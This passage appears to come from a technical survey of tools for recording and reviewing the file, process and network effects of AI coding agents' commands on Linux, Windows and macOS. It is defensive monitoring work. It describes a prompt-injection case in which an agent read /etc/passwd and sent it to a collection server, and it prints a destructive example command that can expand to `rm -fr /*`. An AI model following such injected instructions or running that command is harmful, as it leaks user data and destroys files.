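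In another case, an agent had to download and build a C project. The project's README directed the agent to a web page with a hidden instruction. The agent followed the instruction, reading `/etc/passwd`, the system's list of user accounts, and sending the contents to a collection server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37. The second model gave the record a high attack score because the agent's actions didn't fit its task. The transcript might also have shown this attack, since the agent issued the command itself.

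In the remaining case, which didn't involve hidden effects, a research agent based on GPT-4o mini kept calling a web search tool with the wrong arguments, and AgentSight's second model identified the loop. All three cases are single demonstrations, and none measures how often the second model would raise a false alarm about a harmless session.

Zheng and colleagues measured the overhead with Claude Code on three tasks, running each three times with AgentSight and three times without it.

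| Task | Without AgentSight | With AgentSight | Added time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a repository | 127.98 s | 132.33 s | 3.4% |
| Writing code | 22.54 s | 23.64 s | 4.9% |
| Compiling a repository | 92.40 s | 92.72 s | 0.4% |

The average slowdown is 2.9%, which Zheng and colleagues summarize as under 3%, though two of the three tasks exceed that. Model response times vary from run to run, so three runs can't reliably measure differences of a few seconds or less. Compiling started the most programs and slowed down the least, which suggests that the kernel monitoring adds little overhead. None of the tasks was a large `npm install`.

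AgentSight has since grown from a research prototype into a developer tool. Version 1.0.29, from August 2026, saves each recorded session in a database file, and `agentsight report audit` lists the processes started, files opened and calls to the model. The probes need administrator rights, but the agent still runs as the ordinary user. The database can contain prompts, file paths and web addresses, so Zheng and colleagues advise users to treat it as sensitive.

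AgentSight can't trace Cursor's editor with eBPF. For Cursor, and generally on macOS and Windows, it reads the session files that the agents themselves save, which have the same gaps as any transcript.

### The sample command

Suppose Tetragon is running with the policy above. The script uses `mv`, `rm`, `curl` and `docker`, starts a separate program in the background, and does the rest of its file work in the shell itself.

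| Effect | Tetragon's default events | Added by the policy |
|---|---|---|
| 1. `src/config.json` overwritten | Nothing | Write, with path and process |
| 2. `notes.md` moved | `mv` command with both names | Nothing |
| 3. Temporary file | `rm` command | Write, if the file received any data |
| 4. Line added to `~/.bashrc` | Install script's command and its parents | Write, traceable to npm |
| 5. `.env` read | Nothing | Nothing |
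| 6. HTTPS request | `curl` command with its arguments | Nothing |
| 7. `old.db` deleted | `docker` command and the container's own command | Nothing |
| 8. `cache.bin` written later | Start of the background program | Write, with path and process |

The default events include each program's arguments, which often reveal what the program is about to do. npm runs install scripts through `sh -c`, so if the package's script is a single `echo` command, the event contains the line it adds to `~/.bashrc`. If the script runs a JavaScript file, the event contains only that file's name. The default events would also show little about the HTTPS request if a Node.js program sent it.

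Tetragon monitors the whole machine, so it also logs the command that runs inside the container, along with the container's ID. Unlike strace, it provides direct evidence that something tried to delete `old.db`. As with Audit, a reader still has to match the container's command to the agent's `docker` command by time and arguments.

AgentSight would add the model's reply that requested `./setup.sh`. Its kernel events would include opening `src/config.json`, `.env`, `~/.bashrc` and `cache.bin`, and connecting to the outside server. If the script sent its request through the system's OpenSSL library, the same uprobes could in principle capture the readable text. That text would show whether a key from `.env` left the machine, but AgentSight's database would then contain a copy of any key that was sent.

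## Recording on Windows and macOS workstations

In September 2026, a developer reported on Reddit that Claude Code had deleted 48,218 files from a live Windows project in 103 seconds. The developer had asked the agent to refresh a mirror copy of the project (Antipov, 2026, *«Я кое-что сломал»*). The existing script couldn't update the copy in place, so the agent wrote its own script to delete the old copy. That copy contained 614 junctions, Windows folders that point to other folders. The script followed them into the live project and deleted the files there.

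Most programs treat a junction as an ordinary folder with files in it. A safe cleanup script checks each folder for the marker that identifies a junction and removes the junction without entering it. According to the developer's analysis, the agent's script left the junctions in place and emptied the folders they pointed to.

The script's log listed 55,550 deletions, of which the developer attributed 7,332 to the old copy and 48,218 to the live project. The script also deleted files in `.git`, and the developer had no current copy in a remote repository. The project's history was unrecoverable, according to SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions*. The script had finished by the time the agent told the developer that it had broken something.

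Nobody has independently confirmed the size of the loss, and the Reddit post is no longer online, according to TechRadar's *Do not let programs run commands on your machine*. The mechanism is plausible, though, and cc-safe-setup, a set of safety add-ons for Claude Code, lists a similar earlier report in which a junction in a project folder pointed to the user's home folder and the agent deleted everything in it.

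Few scripts log their own deletions. Without such a log, the developer would have needed a record from Windows itself.

### The NTFS change journal

NTFS, the usual file system on Windows, can keep a change journal for each volume, meaning a drive or partition such as `C:`. Search and backup programs read the journal to find changed files without scanning the whole disk. According to Microsoft's *USN_RECORD_V2 structure (winioctl.h)*, each record includes:

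- a file reference number, which identifies the file or folder
- a parent reference number, which identifies the folder that contains it
- the file's name, without its path
- a time stamp
- reason flags, such as "created", "overwritten", "extended" or "deleted"
- an update sequence number (USN), which gives the record's position in the journal.

The record has no field for the process, the user or the data. It has a `SourceInfo` field, but programs such as virus scanners and replication services set this themselves to mark changes that other software can ignore.

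NTFS adds reason flags as changes accumulate. When `setup.sh` overwrites `src/config.json`, the journal would typically gain three records:

1. The shell opens the file and empties it, and NTFS writes a record with the flag for truncation.
2. The script writes the new contents. NTFS writes a second record with the flags for truncation and extension. Further writes add no records, because the flag for extension is already set.
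3. The shell closes the file. The final record repeats both flags and adds one for closing.

The NTFS change journal shows that a file's contents changed, but not how often a script wrote to it. A move produces two records, one with the old name and parent folder and one with the new. Microsoft's *Change Journal Records* warns that the journal doesn't hold enough information to reverse a change. An administrator can make NTFS track which parts of a large file changed, but the journal still doesn't contain the old data.

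The journal has a target size, and NTFS trims the oldest records when the journal grows too far beyond it. Each record takes 60 bytes plus two for each character of the file's name, so deleting 55,550 files with 20-character names would need about 6 MB, or 12 MB if each deletion produced two records. Microsoft's *How to Modify Allocated Space for a Change Journal* gives 300 MB as the amount that one of its backup products sets aside. A journal of that size would easily hold the whole incident, but weeks of builds and installs could cause NTFS to trim those records.

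A harness with administrator rights could use the journal to list the files that each shell command changed. Microsoft's *fsutil usn* documents the necessary commands:

1. Before the command, the harness runs `fsutil usn queryjournal C:` and saves the next USN.
2. The agent's command runs.
3. The harness runs `fsutil usn readjournal C: startusn=` followed by the saved number, and gets every record added since.

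Reading the journal covers the whole volume, including ignored files and the home folder, without a scan. The harness can also tell that NTFS has trimmed records it needed if the oldest USN left in the journal is higher than the saved one. But the list includes changes by every program on the machine, and the harness can't use the records to separate them.

Microsoft's *Creating, Modifying, and Deleting a Change Journal* explains that an administrator or a service has to create the journal, so a second drive used only for projects may have none.

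### Rebuilding the deleted paths

After a mass deletion, the journal can supply the list of lost files. Each record holds only a name and a parent reference, so a tool has to work out the path. It usually does this with the Master File Table, the NTFS database with an entry for every file and folder, by looking up the parent's entry, then that folder's parent, and so on up to the root folder. According to *ntfs forensics deep dive* (2026), investigators export the journal and the table with the program MFTECmd and join the two on the parent's entry number.

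This fails when the script has deleted the folders too, because NTFS reuses their entries. Khatri (2024), in *NTFS Usnjrnl Rewind*, solves the problem by reading the journal backwards. A reference combines an entry number with a sequence number, which rises by one whenever the file or folder using the entry is deleted. Suppose a script deletes `D:\options\data\prices.csv` and then the folder `data`, and NTFS gives the folder's entry to something else:

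1. The deletion record for `prices.csv` gives the parent as entry 4088, sequence 2. The table now has sequence 3 for that entry, so a direct lookup fails.
2. Reading from the end of the journal, the tool first reaches the deletion of `data`. That record contains the folder's name, its reference (4088, sequence 2) and the reference of its own parent, `options`.
3. `options` still exists, so the tool can work out the path `D:\options\data`.
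4. The tool then reaches the record for `prices.csv`, recognizes the parent reference and completes the path.

The method works because any folder that has disappeared since a file's deletion must have a later record, and NTFS trims the oldest records first. It also corrects wrong paths. In Khatri's example, the usual method placed a deleted program in `C:\temp`, although the `temp` folder was in a user's home folder at the time.

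Junctions don't affect the paths rebuilt from the journal, because the parent reference identifies the folder where a file really was. In the September incident, those paths would have pointed to the live project even though the script had reached the files through the mirror. The developer could have used them to check the count of 48,218 and perhaps to retrieve some files by name from old backups. In the journal, only the timing could have shown that the agent's script was responsible.

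Whether a deleted file's contents can be recovered depends partly on its size. According to IBM's *Disk forensics to uncover exfiltrated file details*, NTFS keeps very small files inside the Master File Table, so their data survives until NTFS reuses the entry. In IBM's test with 5,000 files, about 2,000 names were still recoverable from the table. Larger files are stored outside the table, and a solid-state drive may clear their blocks soon after deletion. The CyberSec Guru's *claude code ai agent data loss mythic society* describes another Claude Code deletion, in which recovery programs could list the file names but found only zeros where the data had been.

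### Event Tracing for Windows

To identify the process behind a deletion, a recorder can use Event Tracing for Windows (ETW), the logging system that Windows uses for its own components. A provider is a part of Windows, or any other program, that can produce events. Separate providers cover processes, file operations and network traffic. Providers normally stay silent until someone starts a session that collects their events:

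1. An administrator starts a session, for example with the `logman` command, and enables the providers for it.
2. When a process deletes a file, the provider puts an event in one of the session's memory buffers. The event has a time stamp and a process ID, along with details such as the path.
3. Windows writes full buffers to a log file or passes them to a program that reads them as they arrive.

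The process that deletes the file doesn't wait for any of this. If events arrive faster than Windows can empty the buffers, the session loses some, as an eBPF monitor does. Each session counts the events it lost, the buffers it failed to write to the log file and the buffers it failed to deliver to a reading program. A harness with its own session can check whether its log is complete, while Linux Audit keeps one count for the whole machine. The ETW counts don't show which process the lost events came from.

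On Windows, a process's start event contains its parent's ID, and an orphaned process keeps that ID rather than getting a new parent as it would on Linux. But once the parent exits, Windows can give its ID to an unrelated program. A recorder has to log every process start and exit, or it may attach the process that wrote `cache.bin` to the wrong branch of the process tree.

In the September incident, the script deleted about 540 files a second, a modest rate for ETW. A running session would have linked those deletions to a process ID, and the process start events would have connected that process to Claude Code. But unlike the change journal, ETW would have helped only if someone had started a session beforehand. Few developers leave file tracing on, because the provider reports activity across the whole machine and the log grows quickly.

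### Sysmon

Sysmon (System Monitor) is a more practical choice for permanent use. This free Microsoft tool installs a driver and a service, and writes selected events to the Windows Event Log. It used to be a separate download, but Microsoft built it into Windows 11 with the March 2026 update, according to TurboGeek's *Windows 11 Now Has Built-In Sysmon*. It is off by default, and an administrator has to enable it (Microsoft, *February 24, 2026—KB5077241*, 2026).

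Sysmon has about 30 event types, and these matter most for an agent:

- Event 1 (process creation) has the full command line, the working folder, the user, and the parent process with its own command line.
- Event 3 (network connection) has the process, the addresses and ports, and the protocol. The administrator has to turn it on.
- Event 5 marks the end of a process.
- Event 11 reports that a process created or overwrote a file.
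- Event 23 reports a deletion and can keep a copy of the file.
- Event 26 reports a deletion without keeping a copy.

Sysmon has no event for reading a file, renaming it or appending to it.

Sysmon gives each process a unique identifier, the ProcessGUID, which avoids the problem of reused process IDs. According to Detection Wiki's *Microsoft-Windows-Sysmon › Event 26*, a deletion event contains this identifier, the user, the program, the file's path and its hashes. If Sysmon had been recording deletions during the September incident, the developer could have searched for the script's ProcessGUID and counted the files it deleted. The hashes would also have shown whether an old copy found elsewhere matched the deleted version.

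The log itself could have been too small, since it has a maximum size and Windows overwrites the oldest events by default. At roughly a kilobyte per event, 55,550 deletions would take about 55 MB, several times what the change journal needs.

### Sysmon's copies of deleted files

When Sysmon logs a file deletion as event 23, it also saves the deleted file in an archive folder on the same volume. In *Sysmon and File Deletion*, Stevens (2020) tested this feature with `sdelete`, a program that overwrites a file before deleting it. Sysmon reported the deletion but kept no copy, because the file contained only zeros by the time Sysmon examined it. The script in the September incident apparently deleted files without overwriting them first, so the archive could have preserved them.

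Restoring the archived files would have taken some work, because Sysmon names each copy after its hash and a developer needs the matching event to find out where the file belongs. If Windows has already overwritten that event, the developer has the copy without its original path. The change journal wouldn't help much, since it doesn't record hashes.

Disk space is the other difficulty, because an archive of every deletion would fill up with temporary files and old build output. Stevens warns against using such a configuration on production systems, so security teams keep copies of fewer files. A sample configuration in techbrunch's *file delete detected* archives executables and scripts, such as `.exe`, `.ps1` and `.js` files, and only logs the deletion of documents. It suits an investigator looking for malware, but a developer who lost a folder of Python code would find nothing in the archive.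 To protect an agent's work, an administrator would need rules for the project folders instead.

Sysmon also doesn't monitor activity inside WSL2, the virtual Linux machine in which many Windows developers run their agents. Windows stores that machine's file system as a single disk file, so neither Sysmon nor the change journal records individual changes inside it. The Linux recorders do work inside WSL2. Antipov notes that Claude Code's built-in sandbox also needs WSL2 to run on Windows.

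### Endpoint Security on macOS

Apple's equivalent is Endpoint Security, an interface introduced with macOS 10.15 in 2019, mainly for antivirus and monitoring products. A client program chooses the types of event it wants, and macOS sends it a message for each matching event. Notification events report something that has already happened. For authorization events, macOS makes the process wait until the client decides whether to allow the operation, as with fanotify's permission events.

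Each authorization message has a deadline, and macOS terminates a client that misses it. Before then, the client could copy the file to keep the pre-image. Unlike fanotify, Endpoint Security also sends authorization messages before deletions, moves and truncation, and its message for an open includes whether the process requested write access. A client could therefore copy only the files at risk.

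Every message includes the responsible process's program file, its code signature and an audit token that distinguishes it from any earlier process with the same ID. It also includes the IDs of the process's original parent and its current parent, which differ if the original exits and macOS assigns a new one. The background process that writes `cache.bin` can therefore still be traced to the script after the shell has returned. Messages about program starts also include the arguments and, for a script run directly, such as `./setup.sh`, the paths of both the script and the shell.

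Messages also carry sequence numbers, one for each event type and one across all types. If a client receives deletion messages 41, 42 and 45, the kernel has dropped two deletion messages, but the numbers don't identify the files involved. If the recorder saves these numbers, a reader can later check the log for gaps, even if the recorder didn't check for them itself.

Few programs can use the interface. The developer must request a permission called an entitlement from Apple and include it in the program's signature. The program must run as root, and the user must give it Full Disk Access in the system settings. These requirements rule out a small open-source recorder that users compile themselves, unless those users weaken their Mac's protections.

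This may be one reason ExecWeave and AgentSight fall back on periodic checks and session files on workstations. Neither method would show which process in a script deleted a particular file.

### eslogger and FSEvents

Since macOS 13, Apple has included `eslogger`, a command that prints Endpoint Security events as text. It already has the entitlement, but it needs root, and the terminal that runs it needs Full Disk Access. This command would record the main effects of a shell command:

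```
sudo eslogger exec fork exit open create write truncate rename unlink close > events.jsonl
```

The output has one line of JSON, a structured text format, for each event. A shortened line for the deletion of the temporary file could look like this:

```
{"seq_num":41,"process":{"audit_token":{"pid":4131},"original_ppid":4102,"executable":{"path":"/bin/rm"}},"event":{"unlink":{"target":{"path":"/Users/ana/app/setup.tmp"}}}}
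```

The `process` part identifies `rm`, with process 4102 as its original parent. `unlink` is the system's name for a deletion. `eslogger` only receives notifications, so it can't pause a process to save a file. Apple doesn't promise to keep the format stable. `eslogger` leaves out events from its own process group to avoid recording its own output in a loop, so if a harness starts `eslogger` and the agent in the same group, the log will omit the agent's events.

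Endpoint Security has no events for internet connections. It reports connections to local sockets, such as the one that `docker` uses, but if `curl` made an HTTPS request, the log would show only that `curl` started and with what arguments. If a Node.js program that was already running sent the request, the log would have no event for it. Apple handles network monitoring in a separate framework, Network Extension, which requires its own entitlement and user approval.

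FSEvents is an older and simpler macOS facility, similar in purpose to the NTFS change journal. It reports which files or folders have changed, and macOS saves the events on each volume, so a program can look up what changed while it was not running. An ordinary program can use it without root or an entitlement. It covers a whole folder tree, whereas inotify needs a separate watch for each folder.

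An FSEvents entry has a path and flags, but no process, time of change or content. macOS can merge several changes to a file into one entry, and the flags then don't show the order of the changes. If macOS drops events, it sets a flag to indicate that the program should scan the folder again.

### The sample command

Suppose the agent runs `./setup.sh` in Git Bash, a version of bash for Windows, and all the files are on one NTFS volume. `~/.bashrc` is then in the Windows home folder, and Docker shares the folder containing `old.db` from that volume. An ETW session records processes, files and connections, and Sysmon is set to log file creation, file deletion and network events.

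| Effect | Change journal | ETW | Sysmon |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. `src/config.json` overwritten | Truncated and extended | Write, with process ID | File overwritten, with process |
| 2. `notes.md` moved | Old and new names | Rename, with process ID | `mv` command with both names |
| 3. Temporary file | Created and deleted | Both, with process ID | Both, with process |
| 4. Line added to `~/.bashrc` | Extended | Write, with process ID | Install script's command and its parents |
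| 5. `.env` read | Nothing | Open and read, with process ID | Nothing |
| 6. HTTPS request | Nothing | Connection, with process ID | Connection, with process |
| 7. `old.db` deleted | Deleted | Deletion by another process | `docker` command; deletion by another process |
| 8. `cache.bin` written later | Created and extended | Write, with process ID | File created, with process |

Only Sysmon could preserve any old file contents, and for this command its archive would hold at most the temporary file and `old.db`. The process that serves Windows folders to Docker's virtual machine deletes `old.db`, so neither ETW nor Sysmon connects the deletion to the agent.

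On a Mac, suppose `eslogger` runs with the events listed above and Docker again shares the folder with `old.db`.

| Effect | Endpoint Security through `eslogger` | FSEvents |
|---|---|---|
| 1. `src/config.json` overwritten | Write, with process and original parent | Modified |
| 2. `notes.md` moved | One event with both names | Two renamed paths |
| 3. Temporary file | Created and deleted, with process | Created and removed, perhaps in one entry |
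| 4. Line added to `~/.bashrc` | Write, traceable to npm | Modified |
| 5. `.env` read | Opened for reading, with process | Nothing |
| 6. HTTPS request | `curl` command with its arguments | Nothing |
| 7. `old.db` deleted | `docker` command; deletion by another process | Removed |
| 8. `cache.bin` written later | Write, with process and original parent | Created and modified |

Adding `uipc_connect` to the `eslogger` command would also record the `docker` program's connection to its local socket, but it wouldn't link that connection to the deletion.

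## Comparing files before and after with OverlayFS, ZFS, Btrfs and APFS

Most event recorders don't keep a file's old contents, and shadow repositories leave out ignored files and everything outside the project. File systems can preserve all of these. OverlayFS, part of the Linux kernel, diverts a command's changes into a separate folder. ZFS, Btrfs and Apple's APFS can snapshot a whole volume before a command runs, so a tool can compare the snapshot with the volume afterward.

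### What OverlayFS writes down

OverlayFS combines two folder trees into a third. The lower layer holds the existing files, and OverlayFS never changes it. The upper layer starts out empty and receives every change. Programs work in the merged view, where a file in the upper layer hides any file with the same path in the lower one. If both layers have a folder with the same path, the merged view combines their contents. Brown's *Overlay Filesystem*, part of the kernel's documentation, gives a mount command of this form:

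```
mount -t overlay overlay -olowerdir=/home/ana/demo,upperdir=/tmp/up,workdir=/tmp/work /mnt/demo
```

The `workdir` is an empty folder that OverlayFS needs for its own use. Suppose `demo` contains `app.conf`, `notes.md`, `old.log`, a folder `docs`, and a folder `build` with the files `a.o` and `b.o`. An agent runs these commands in `/mnt/demo`, the merged view:

```
echo "hello" > new.txt
echo "debug=1" >> app.conf
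rm old.log
rm -r build && mkdir build && echo "x" > build/c.o
mv notes.md docs/notes.md
```

Each command affects the upper layer differently:

1. **Create.** `new.txt` goes straight into the upper layer.
2. **Edit in place.** When the shell opens `app.conf` for writing, OverlayFS copies the whole file to the upper layer, an operation called copy-up. The shell then adds its line to the copy. Later writes go to the same copy. Docker points out that OverlayFS copies a large file in full even if a program changes only a small part of it.
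3. **Delete.** OverlayFS can't remove `old.log` from the lower layer, so it puts a whiteout in the upper one. This is a marker, usually a device file with the number 0/0, that hides the file from the merged view.
4. **Replace a folder.** `rm -r` leaves a whiteout for `build`, and `mkdir` replaces it with a new folder marked as opaque. The mark makes OverlayFS ignore the old `build`. Without it, `a.o` and `b.o` would reappear beside `c.o`.
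5. **Rename a file.** OverlayFS copies all of `notes.md` to the upper layer, where it ends up as `docs/notes.md`, and leaves a whiteout at the old path.

A shortened listing of the upper layer would look like this:

```
-rw-r--r--   app.conf
drwxr-xr-x   build/          trusted.overlay.opaque="y"
-rw-r--r--   build/c.o
drwxr-xr-x   docs/
-rw-r--r--   docs/notes.md
-rw-r--r--   new.txt
c---------   notes.md        0, 0
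c---------   old.log         0, 0
```

To turn this into a list of changes, a program looks up each path in the lower layer. A whiteout means that a command deleted the file. Any other file is a change if the lower layer has the same path, and a new file if it doesn't. For an opaque folder, the program also has to list everything in the old folder that is missing from the new one. In the letters that `docker diff` uses (A for added, C for changed, D for deleted), the result is:

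```
C /app.conf
C /build
D /build/a.o
D /build/b.o
A /build/c.o
C /docs
A /docs/notes.md
A /new.txt
D /notes.md
D /old.log
```

`docker diff` lists the files and folders that have changed in a container since Docker created it, with the container's image as the lower layer. In Docker's example, the web server nginx has added `/run/nginx.pid`, so the list also marks the folder `/run` as changed. The list doesn't show which process made each change, when it happened or what the files contain, but the image still has the old version of each changed or deleted file.

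The upper layer contains little besides the changes, so this method doesn't have to search the whole project for them as a Git scan does. It also ignores `.gitignore`, so the deletion of an untracked `data/` folder would appear like any other deletion.

### Where the upper layer misleads

Some files in the upper layer are identical to the originals because OverlayFS copies a file up when a program opens it for reading and writing, even if the program never writes to it. The `sqlite3` command normally opens a database this way, so a read-only query can put a full copy of the database in the upper layer. A tool that checks only paths would report the database as changed. Comparing the contents of the two copies removes the false entry but takes time for large files.

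A renamed file looks like a deletion and a creation. By default, renaming a folder from the lower layer of OverlayFS fails with `EXDEV`, an error that normally means the two paths are on different file systems. `mv` responds by copying the folder's contents and deleting the original, so renaming `src` to `lib` produces a whiteout for `src` and a new copy of every file in it. A program that doesn't handle `EXDEV` fails, although it would have worked on an ordinary file system.

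The optional `redirect_dir` feature avoids the copying. OverlayFS then creates only the folder itself at the new path, with an attribute that records the original location. A tool that doesn't read the attribute would report an empty new folder.

OverlayFS can also change a command's result when a file has hard links. If `a.txt` and `b.txt` are two names for one file, a write to `a.txt` normally appears under both. By default, OverlayFS copies up only `a.txt`, so `b.txt` keeps the old contents.

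The temporary file from the sample command leaves no entry. It exists only in the upper layer, so `rm` deletes it without needing a whiteout to hide a lower-layer copy.

The upper layer also combines the changes from all the commands that ran in it. If one command deletes `app.conf` and a later one recreates it, the list contains only one changed file. A harness could give each command its own upper layer and use the layers from earlier commands as additional lower layers, but Docker warns that searching through many layers can slow file access. YoloFS, the file system by Zhong and colleagues, uses a different layout to keep many intermediate states without slowing ordinary file operations.

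The method is good at attributing changes because only programs that work in the merged view write to the upper layer. The developer's edits in the original folder therefore don't appear among the agent's changes. But Brown warns that nobody may change the lower layer while OverlayFS is using it, because the results are undefined. Even if nothing goes wrong during the run, accepting the agent's changes can erase the developer's edits. If the agent edits `app.conf` in the merged view and the developer then edits the original, copying the agent's version back would overwrite the developer's edit unless the tool checks for it first.

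### Reviewing changes with try

*Controlling Opaque-Component Effects with Semisolates and Try* (Lamprou, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) presents `try`, a shell tool that turns this method into a single command. A user puts `try` in front of a command, and the tool runs the command over an overlay and lists its file changes. The user can then apply all, some or none of them.

One of their examples is a script, of the kind a language model might write, that should empty the folder it is in:

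```
rm -fr "$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"/*
```

`${0%/*}` should give the script's folder, but it gives `delete.sh` if the user runs `sh delete.sh` from that folder. `cd` then fails, the part in quotation marks is empty, and the shell runs `rm -fr /*`. If the user puts `try` in front of the command, `try` lists `/home (deleted)` and `/etc (deleted)` and leaves the real folders untouched.

For `try ./setup.sh`, the steps are:

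1. `try` creates temporary folders for the upper layers.
2. It enters new namespaces, a kernel feature that gives processes their own view of resources such as mounted file systems and process IDs. This is why `try` doesn't need administrator rights, provided the system lets ordinary users create namespaces.
3. It sets up a separate overlay for each top-level folder, such as `/home`, `/etc` and `/srv`. One overlay for the whole disk would not work, because OverlayFS doesn't allow the upper layer to overlap the lower one.
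4. It runs the script in the merged view.
5. It reads the upper layers, prints the list and asks the user what to do.
6. If the user accepts, it moves the new and changed files to their real locations and deletes the originals that have whiteouts.

`try` therefore covers `~/.bashrc` as well as the project. The `-N` option saves a command's changes under a name without applying them, and `-L` lets a later command run on top of them. A harness could use these options to keep a separate change set for each shell command. With `-t`, `try` also runs strace and logs the files the command opened.

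Lamprou and colleagues tested `try` on 25 benchmarks. In all of them, the command produced the same output as an ordinary run, and the files were the same once `try` had applied the changes. They also compared `try` with the built-in dry-run modes of five commands, which describe what a command would do without doing it. `try` reported the same file changes with two exceptions, one of which was a rename that `try` listed as a deletion and a creation.

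Five scripts that ChatGPT had generated took 1.1 to 1.9 times as long under `try`. A program that created no files took 165 milliseconds, mostly for setting up and removing the overlay. Creating 10,000 tiny files took 11 seconds, including 6.3 seconds to leave the namespace at the end. A large `npm install` is more like that test than like the scripts, so its delay at the end could be noticeable.

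The namespaces also change how some programs behave. A command under `try` appears to run as root but can't switch to another user, so a script that uses `sudo` to install a system package may fail. The command can write to files whose permissions would normally forbid it, so the list may include changes that an ordinary run could not have made. Lamprou and colleagues warn that npm may behave differently when it appears to run as root.

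`try` can't hold back an HTTPS request or an email. The `-x` option disables the network, but then `npm install` can't download anything. Lamprou and colleagues designed the tool to guard against mistakes, not against malicious programs that know about `try` and attempt to evade it.

### Use with coding agents

Several students wrapped whole agent sessions in `try` and reviewed the file changes before accepting them. Lamprou and colleagues report that this helped when an agent acted on misleading information from the web. They also describe users who discarded a command's effects because it had written outside the expected folder or changed more files than expected. These reports are anecdotal. Long lists of changes are known to be hard to review. An add-on called `try-summarize` sends the list to a language model, which describes the most important changes first and points out any in sensitive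 folders.

The sandboxes in the major harnesses mostly limit which files a command can reach and let permitted changes go straight to the real files. According to Zhong and colleagues, Claude Code and VS Code's Copilot offer one such sandbox, Bubblewrap, as an option, while Codex and Cursor use another, Landlock, by default. OpenCode has no sandbox.

Gemini CLI offers Docker as an option, so `docker diff` could list what a command changed inside the container. But a container usually accesses a project through a folder mounted from the host, and changes there bypass the container's writable layer. The list could therefore include a changed `.bashrc` in the container but not a changed `src/config.json` in the mounted project.

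YoloFS stages an agent's changes until the user accepts them, and Zhong and colleagues have connected it to Claude Code, Copilot and Gemini.

Capturing file changes is harder on macOS, which doesn't have OverlayFS. According to docs.rs' *oops-sh 0.2.0*, the small undo tool oops lets commands change the real files on macOS, then looks for files whose size or modification time has changed. It misses a change if the command restores the file's old size and modification time. Services such as Dropbox or iCloud Drive may also copy the changes to other devices before the user undoes them.

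### How a snapshot keeps old data

An OverlayFS mount and a snapshot both have to exist before the command starts. With OverlayFS, the command has to run inside the merged view, but with a snapshot, it can work on the real files as usual.

ZFS, Btrfs and APFS write changed data to free blocks instead of overwriting the old ones. A snapshot makes the file system keep the old blocks. The Eclectic Light Company's *Take control of snapshots* (2026) gives the example of a file in blocks 1 to 4. After a snapshot, a program edits the last two blocks, and APFS writes the new data to blocks 5 and 6. The current file now consists of blocks 1, 2, 5 and 6, while the snapshot still refers to blocks 1 to 4. If the user deletes the file, only blocks 5 and 6 become free.

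A snapshot is small at first and grows as files change. The Eclectic Light Company warns that a forgotten one can reach hundreds of gigabytes. A harness that took a snapshot before every shell command would also have to delete old ones.

### zfs diff

ZFS takes snapshots of datasets, which are parts of its storage that an administrator can manage separately, much like partitions. `zfs diff` compares a snapshot with a later one or with the current files. Suppose `demo` is a dataset at `/tank/demo`, and the agent runs the commands from the OverlayFS example directly in it after an administrator has taken a snapshot called `before`. In the format that OpenZFS's *zfs-diff.8* (2022) describes, the output would include lines like these:

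```
# zfs diff -F tank/demo@before tank/demo
M       /       /tank/demo/
M       F       /tank/demo/app.conf
+       F       /tank/demo/new.txt
-       F       /tank/demo/old.log
M       /       /tank/demo/docs
R       F       /tank/demo/notes.md -> /tank/demo/docs/notes.md
```

The first column shows the type of change: modified, renamed, deleted (`-`) or created (`+`). The second distinguishes folders (`/`) from ordinary files (`F`). The folder `/tank/demo/` counts as modified because the names in it changed. If a file gains or loses a hard link, the output also shows the change in its link count.

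Unlike the upper layer of an overlay, the output shows the rename with both names. It doesn't show what changed inside `app.conf`, but a reader can compare the file with the old version in the snapshot.

### An incremental btrfs send stream

Btrfs has no direct equivalent of `zfs diff`, but its backup command can serve as one. `btrfs send` produces a stream of instructions for rebuilding a snapshot on another disk. With the `-p` option and an earlier snapshot, the stream contains only the instructions that turn the old state into the new one. For a project in its own subvolume, the Btrfs counterpart of a dataset, the commands could be:

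```
btrfs subvolume snapshot -r demo before
(the agent's command runs)
btrfs subvolume snapshot -r demo after
btrfs send --no-data -p before after | btrfs receive --dump
```

The `-r` option makes the snapshots read-only, which *btrfs-send(8)* requires. `--no-data` leaves out the files' contents. With `--dump`, Btrfs prints one instruction per line and changes nothing on the disk. For the commands in the small `demo` project, the output would include lines like these, in shortened form:

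```
link            ./docs/notes.md        dest=notes.md
unlink          ./notes.md
update_extent   ./app.conf             offset=0 len=820
unlink          ./old.log
mkfile          ./o-290-45678
rename          ./o-290-45678          dest=./new.txt
```

The first two lines record the move of `notes.md`. Btrfs typically gives the file a second name and then removes the first. `update_extent` shows which part of a file has new data. Creating `new.txt` takes the last two lines because the stream always creates a file under a special name and then renames it, as Btrfs' *Send stream format* explains. Other instructions cover changed permissions, owners and time stamps.

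The stream contains the difference between the two snapshots, not a log of what the agent's command did. No program created a file called `o-290-45678`, and the order of the lines doesn't show which change came first. If a program wrote to `app.conf` fifty times, the stream contains only the net change. Without `--no-data`, it also contains the new data, while the old data stays in the first snapshot.

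### APFS snapshots and tmutil

On a Mac, `tmutil localsnapshot` takes a snapshot of every volume that Time Machine, Apple's backup program, backs up. If Time Machine is off, the command covers only the Data volume, which holds the user's files. The Eclectic Light Company's *Last Week on My Mac* (2026) points out that the command can't take a snapshot of any other volume, such as an external drive that holds a project but that Time Machine doesn't back up. macOS deletes these snapshots after 24 hours, or sooner if space runs low.

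macOS has no convenient counterpart to `zfs diff`. `tmutil` has a `compare` command, which the manual page *TMUTIL(8)* describes as a comparison of backups. In the Apple forum thread *Compare two localsnapshots in APFS*, a developer mounted a local snapshot but couldn't get `compare` to accept it. A later reply blamed a missing Full Disk Access permission for such errors. The thread's other suggestion is to mount the snapshot and use an ordinary comparison tool, which has to go through both folder trees.

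A harness could shorten that search by getting the list of changed paths from FSEvents, then reading the old contents from the snapshot. Time Machine normally uses the FSEvents database to decide what to back up, although it compared snapshots in macOS High Sierra, according to The Eclectic Light Company's *What is a snapshot, and how does it work?* (2024).

A user can easily restore single files by mounting the snapshot in Disk Utility and copying them out. Rolling back the whole volume requires restarting the Mac in Recovery mode and deletes all later snapshots.

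A harness can't take and roll back APFS snapshots by itself. Apple's *fs_snapshot_create.2* states that the snapshot functions need administrator rights and an entitlement. Rollback needs a separate entitlement, and the Eclectic Light Company knows of no developer outside Apple who has it. In the forum thread *APFS snapshot revert*, an Apple engineer wrote that Apple had no tool or programming interface for rollback.

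### Missing volumes and other people's changes

A snapshot covers only the volume, dataset or subvolume that someone chose. If the home folder and `/srv/data` are in separate ZFS datasets, a snapshot of the home folder's dataset can't show the deletion of `/srv/data/old.db`. An administrator can snapshot both, but has to know in advance where a script might make changes.

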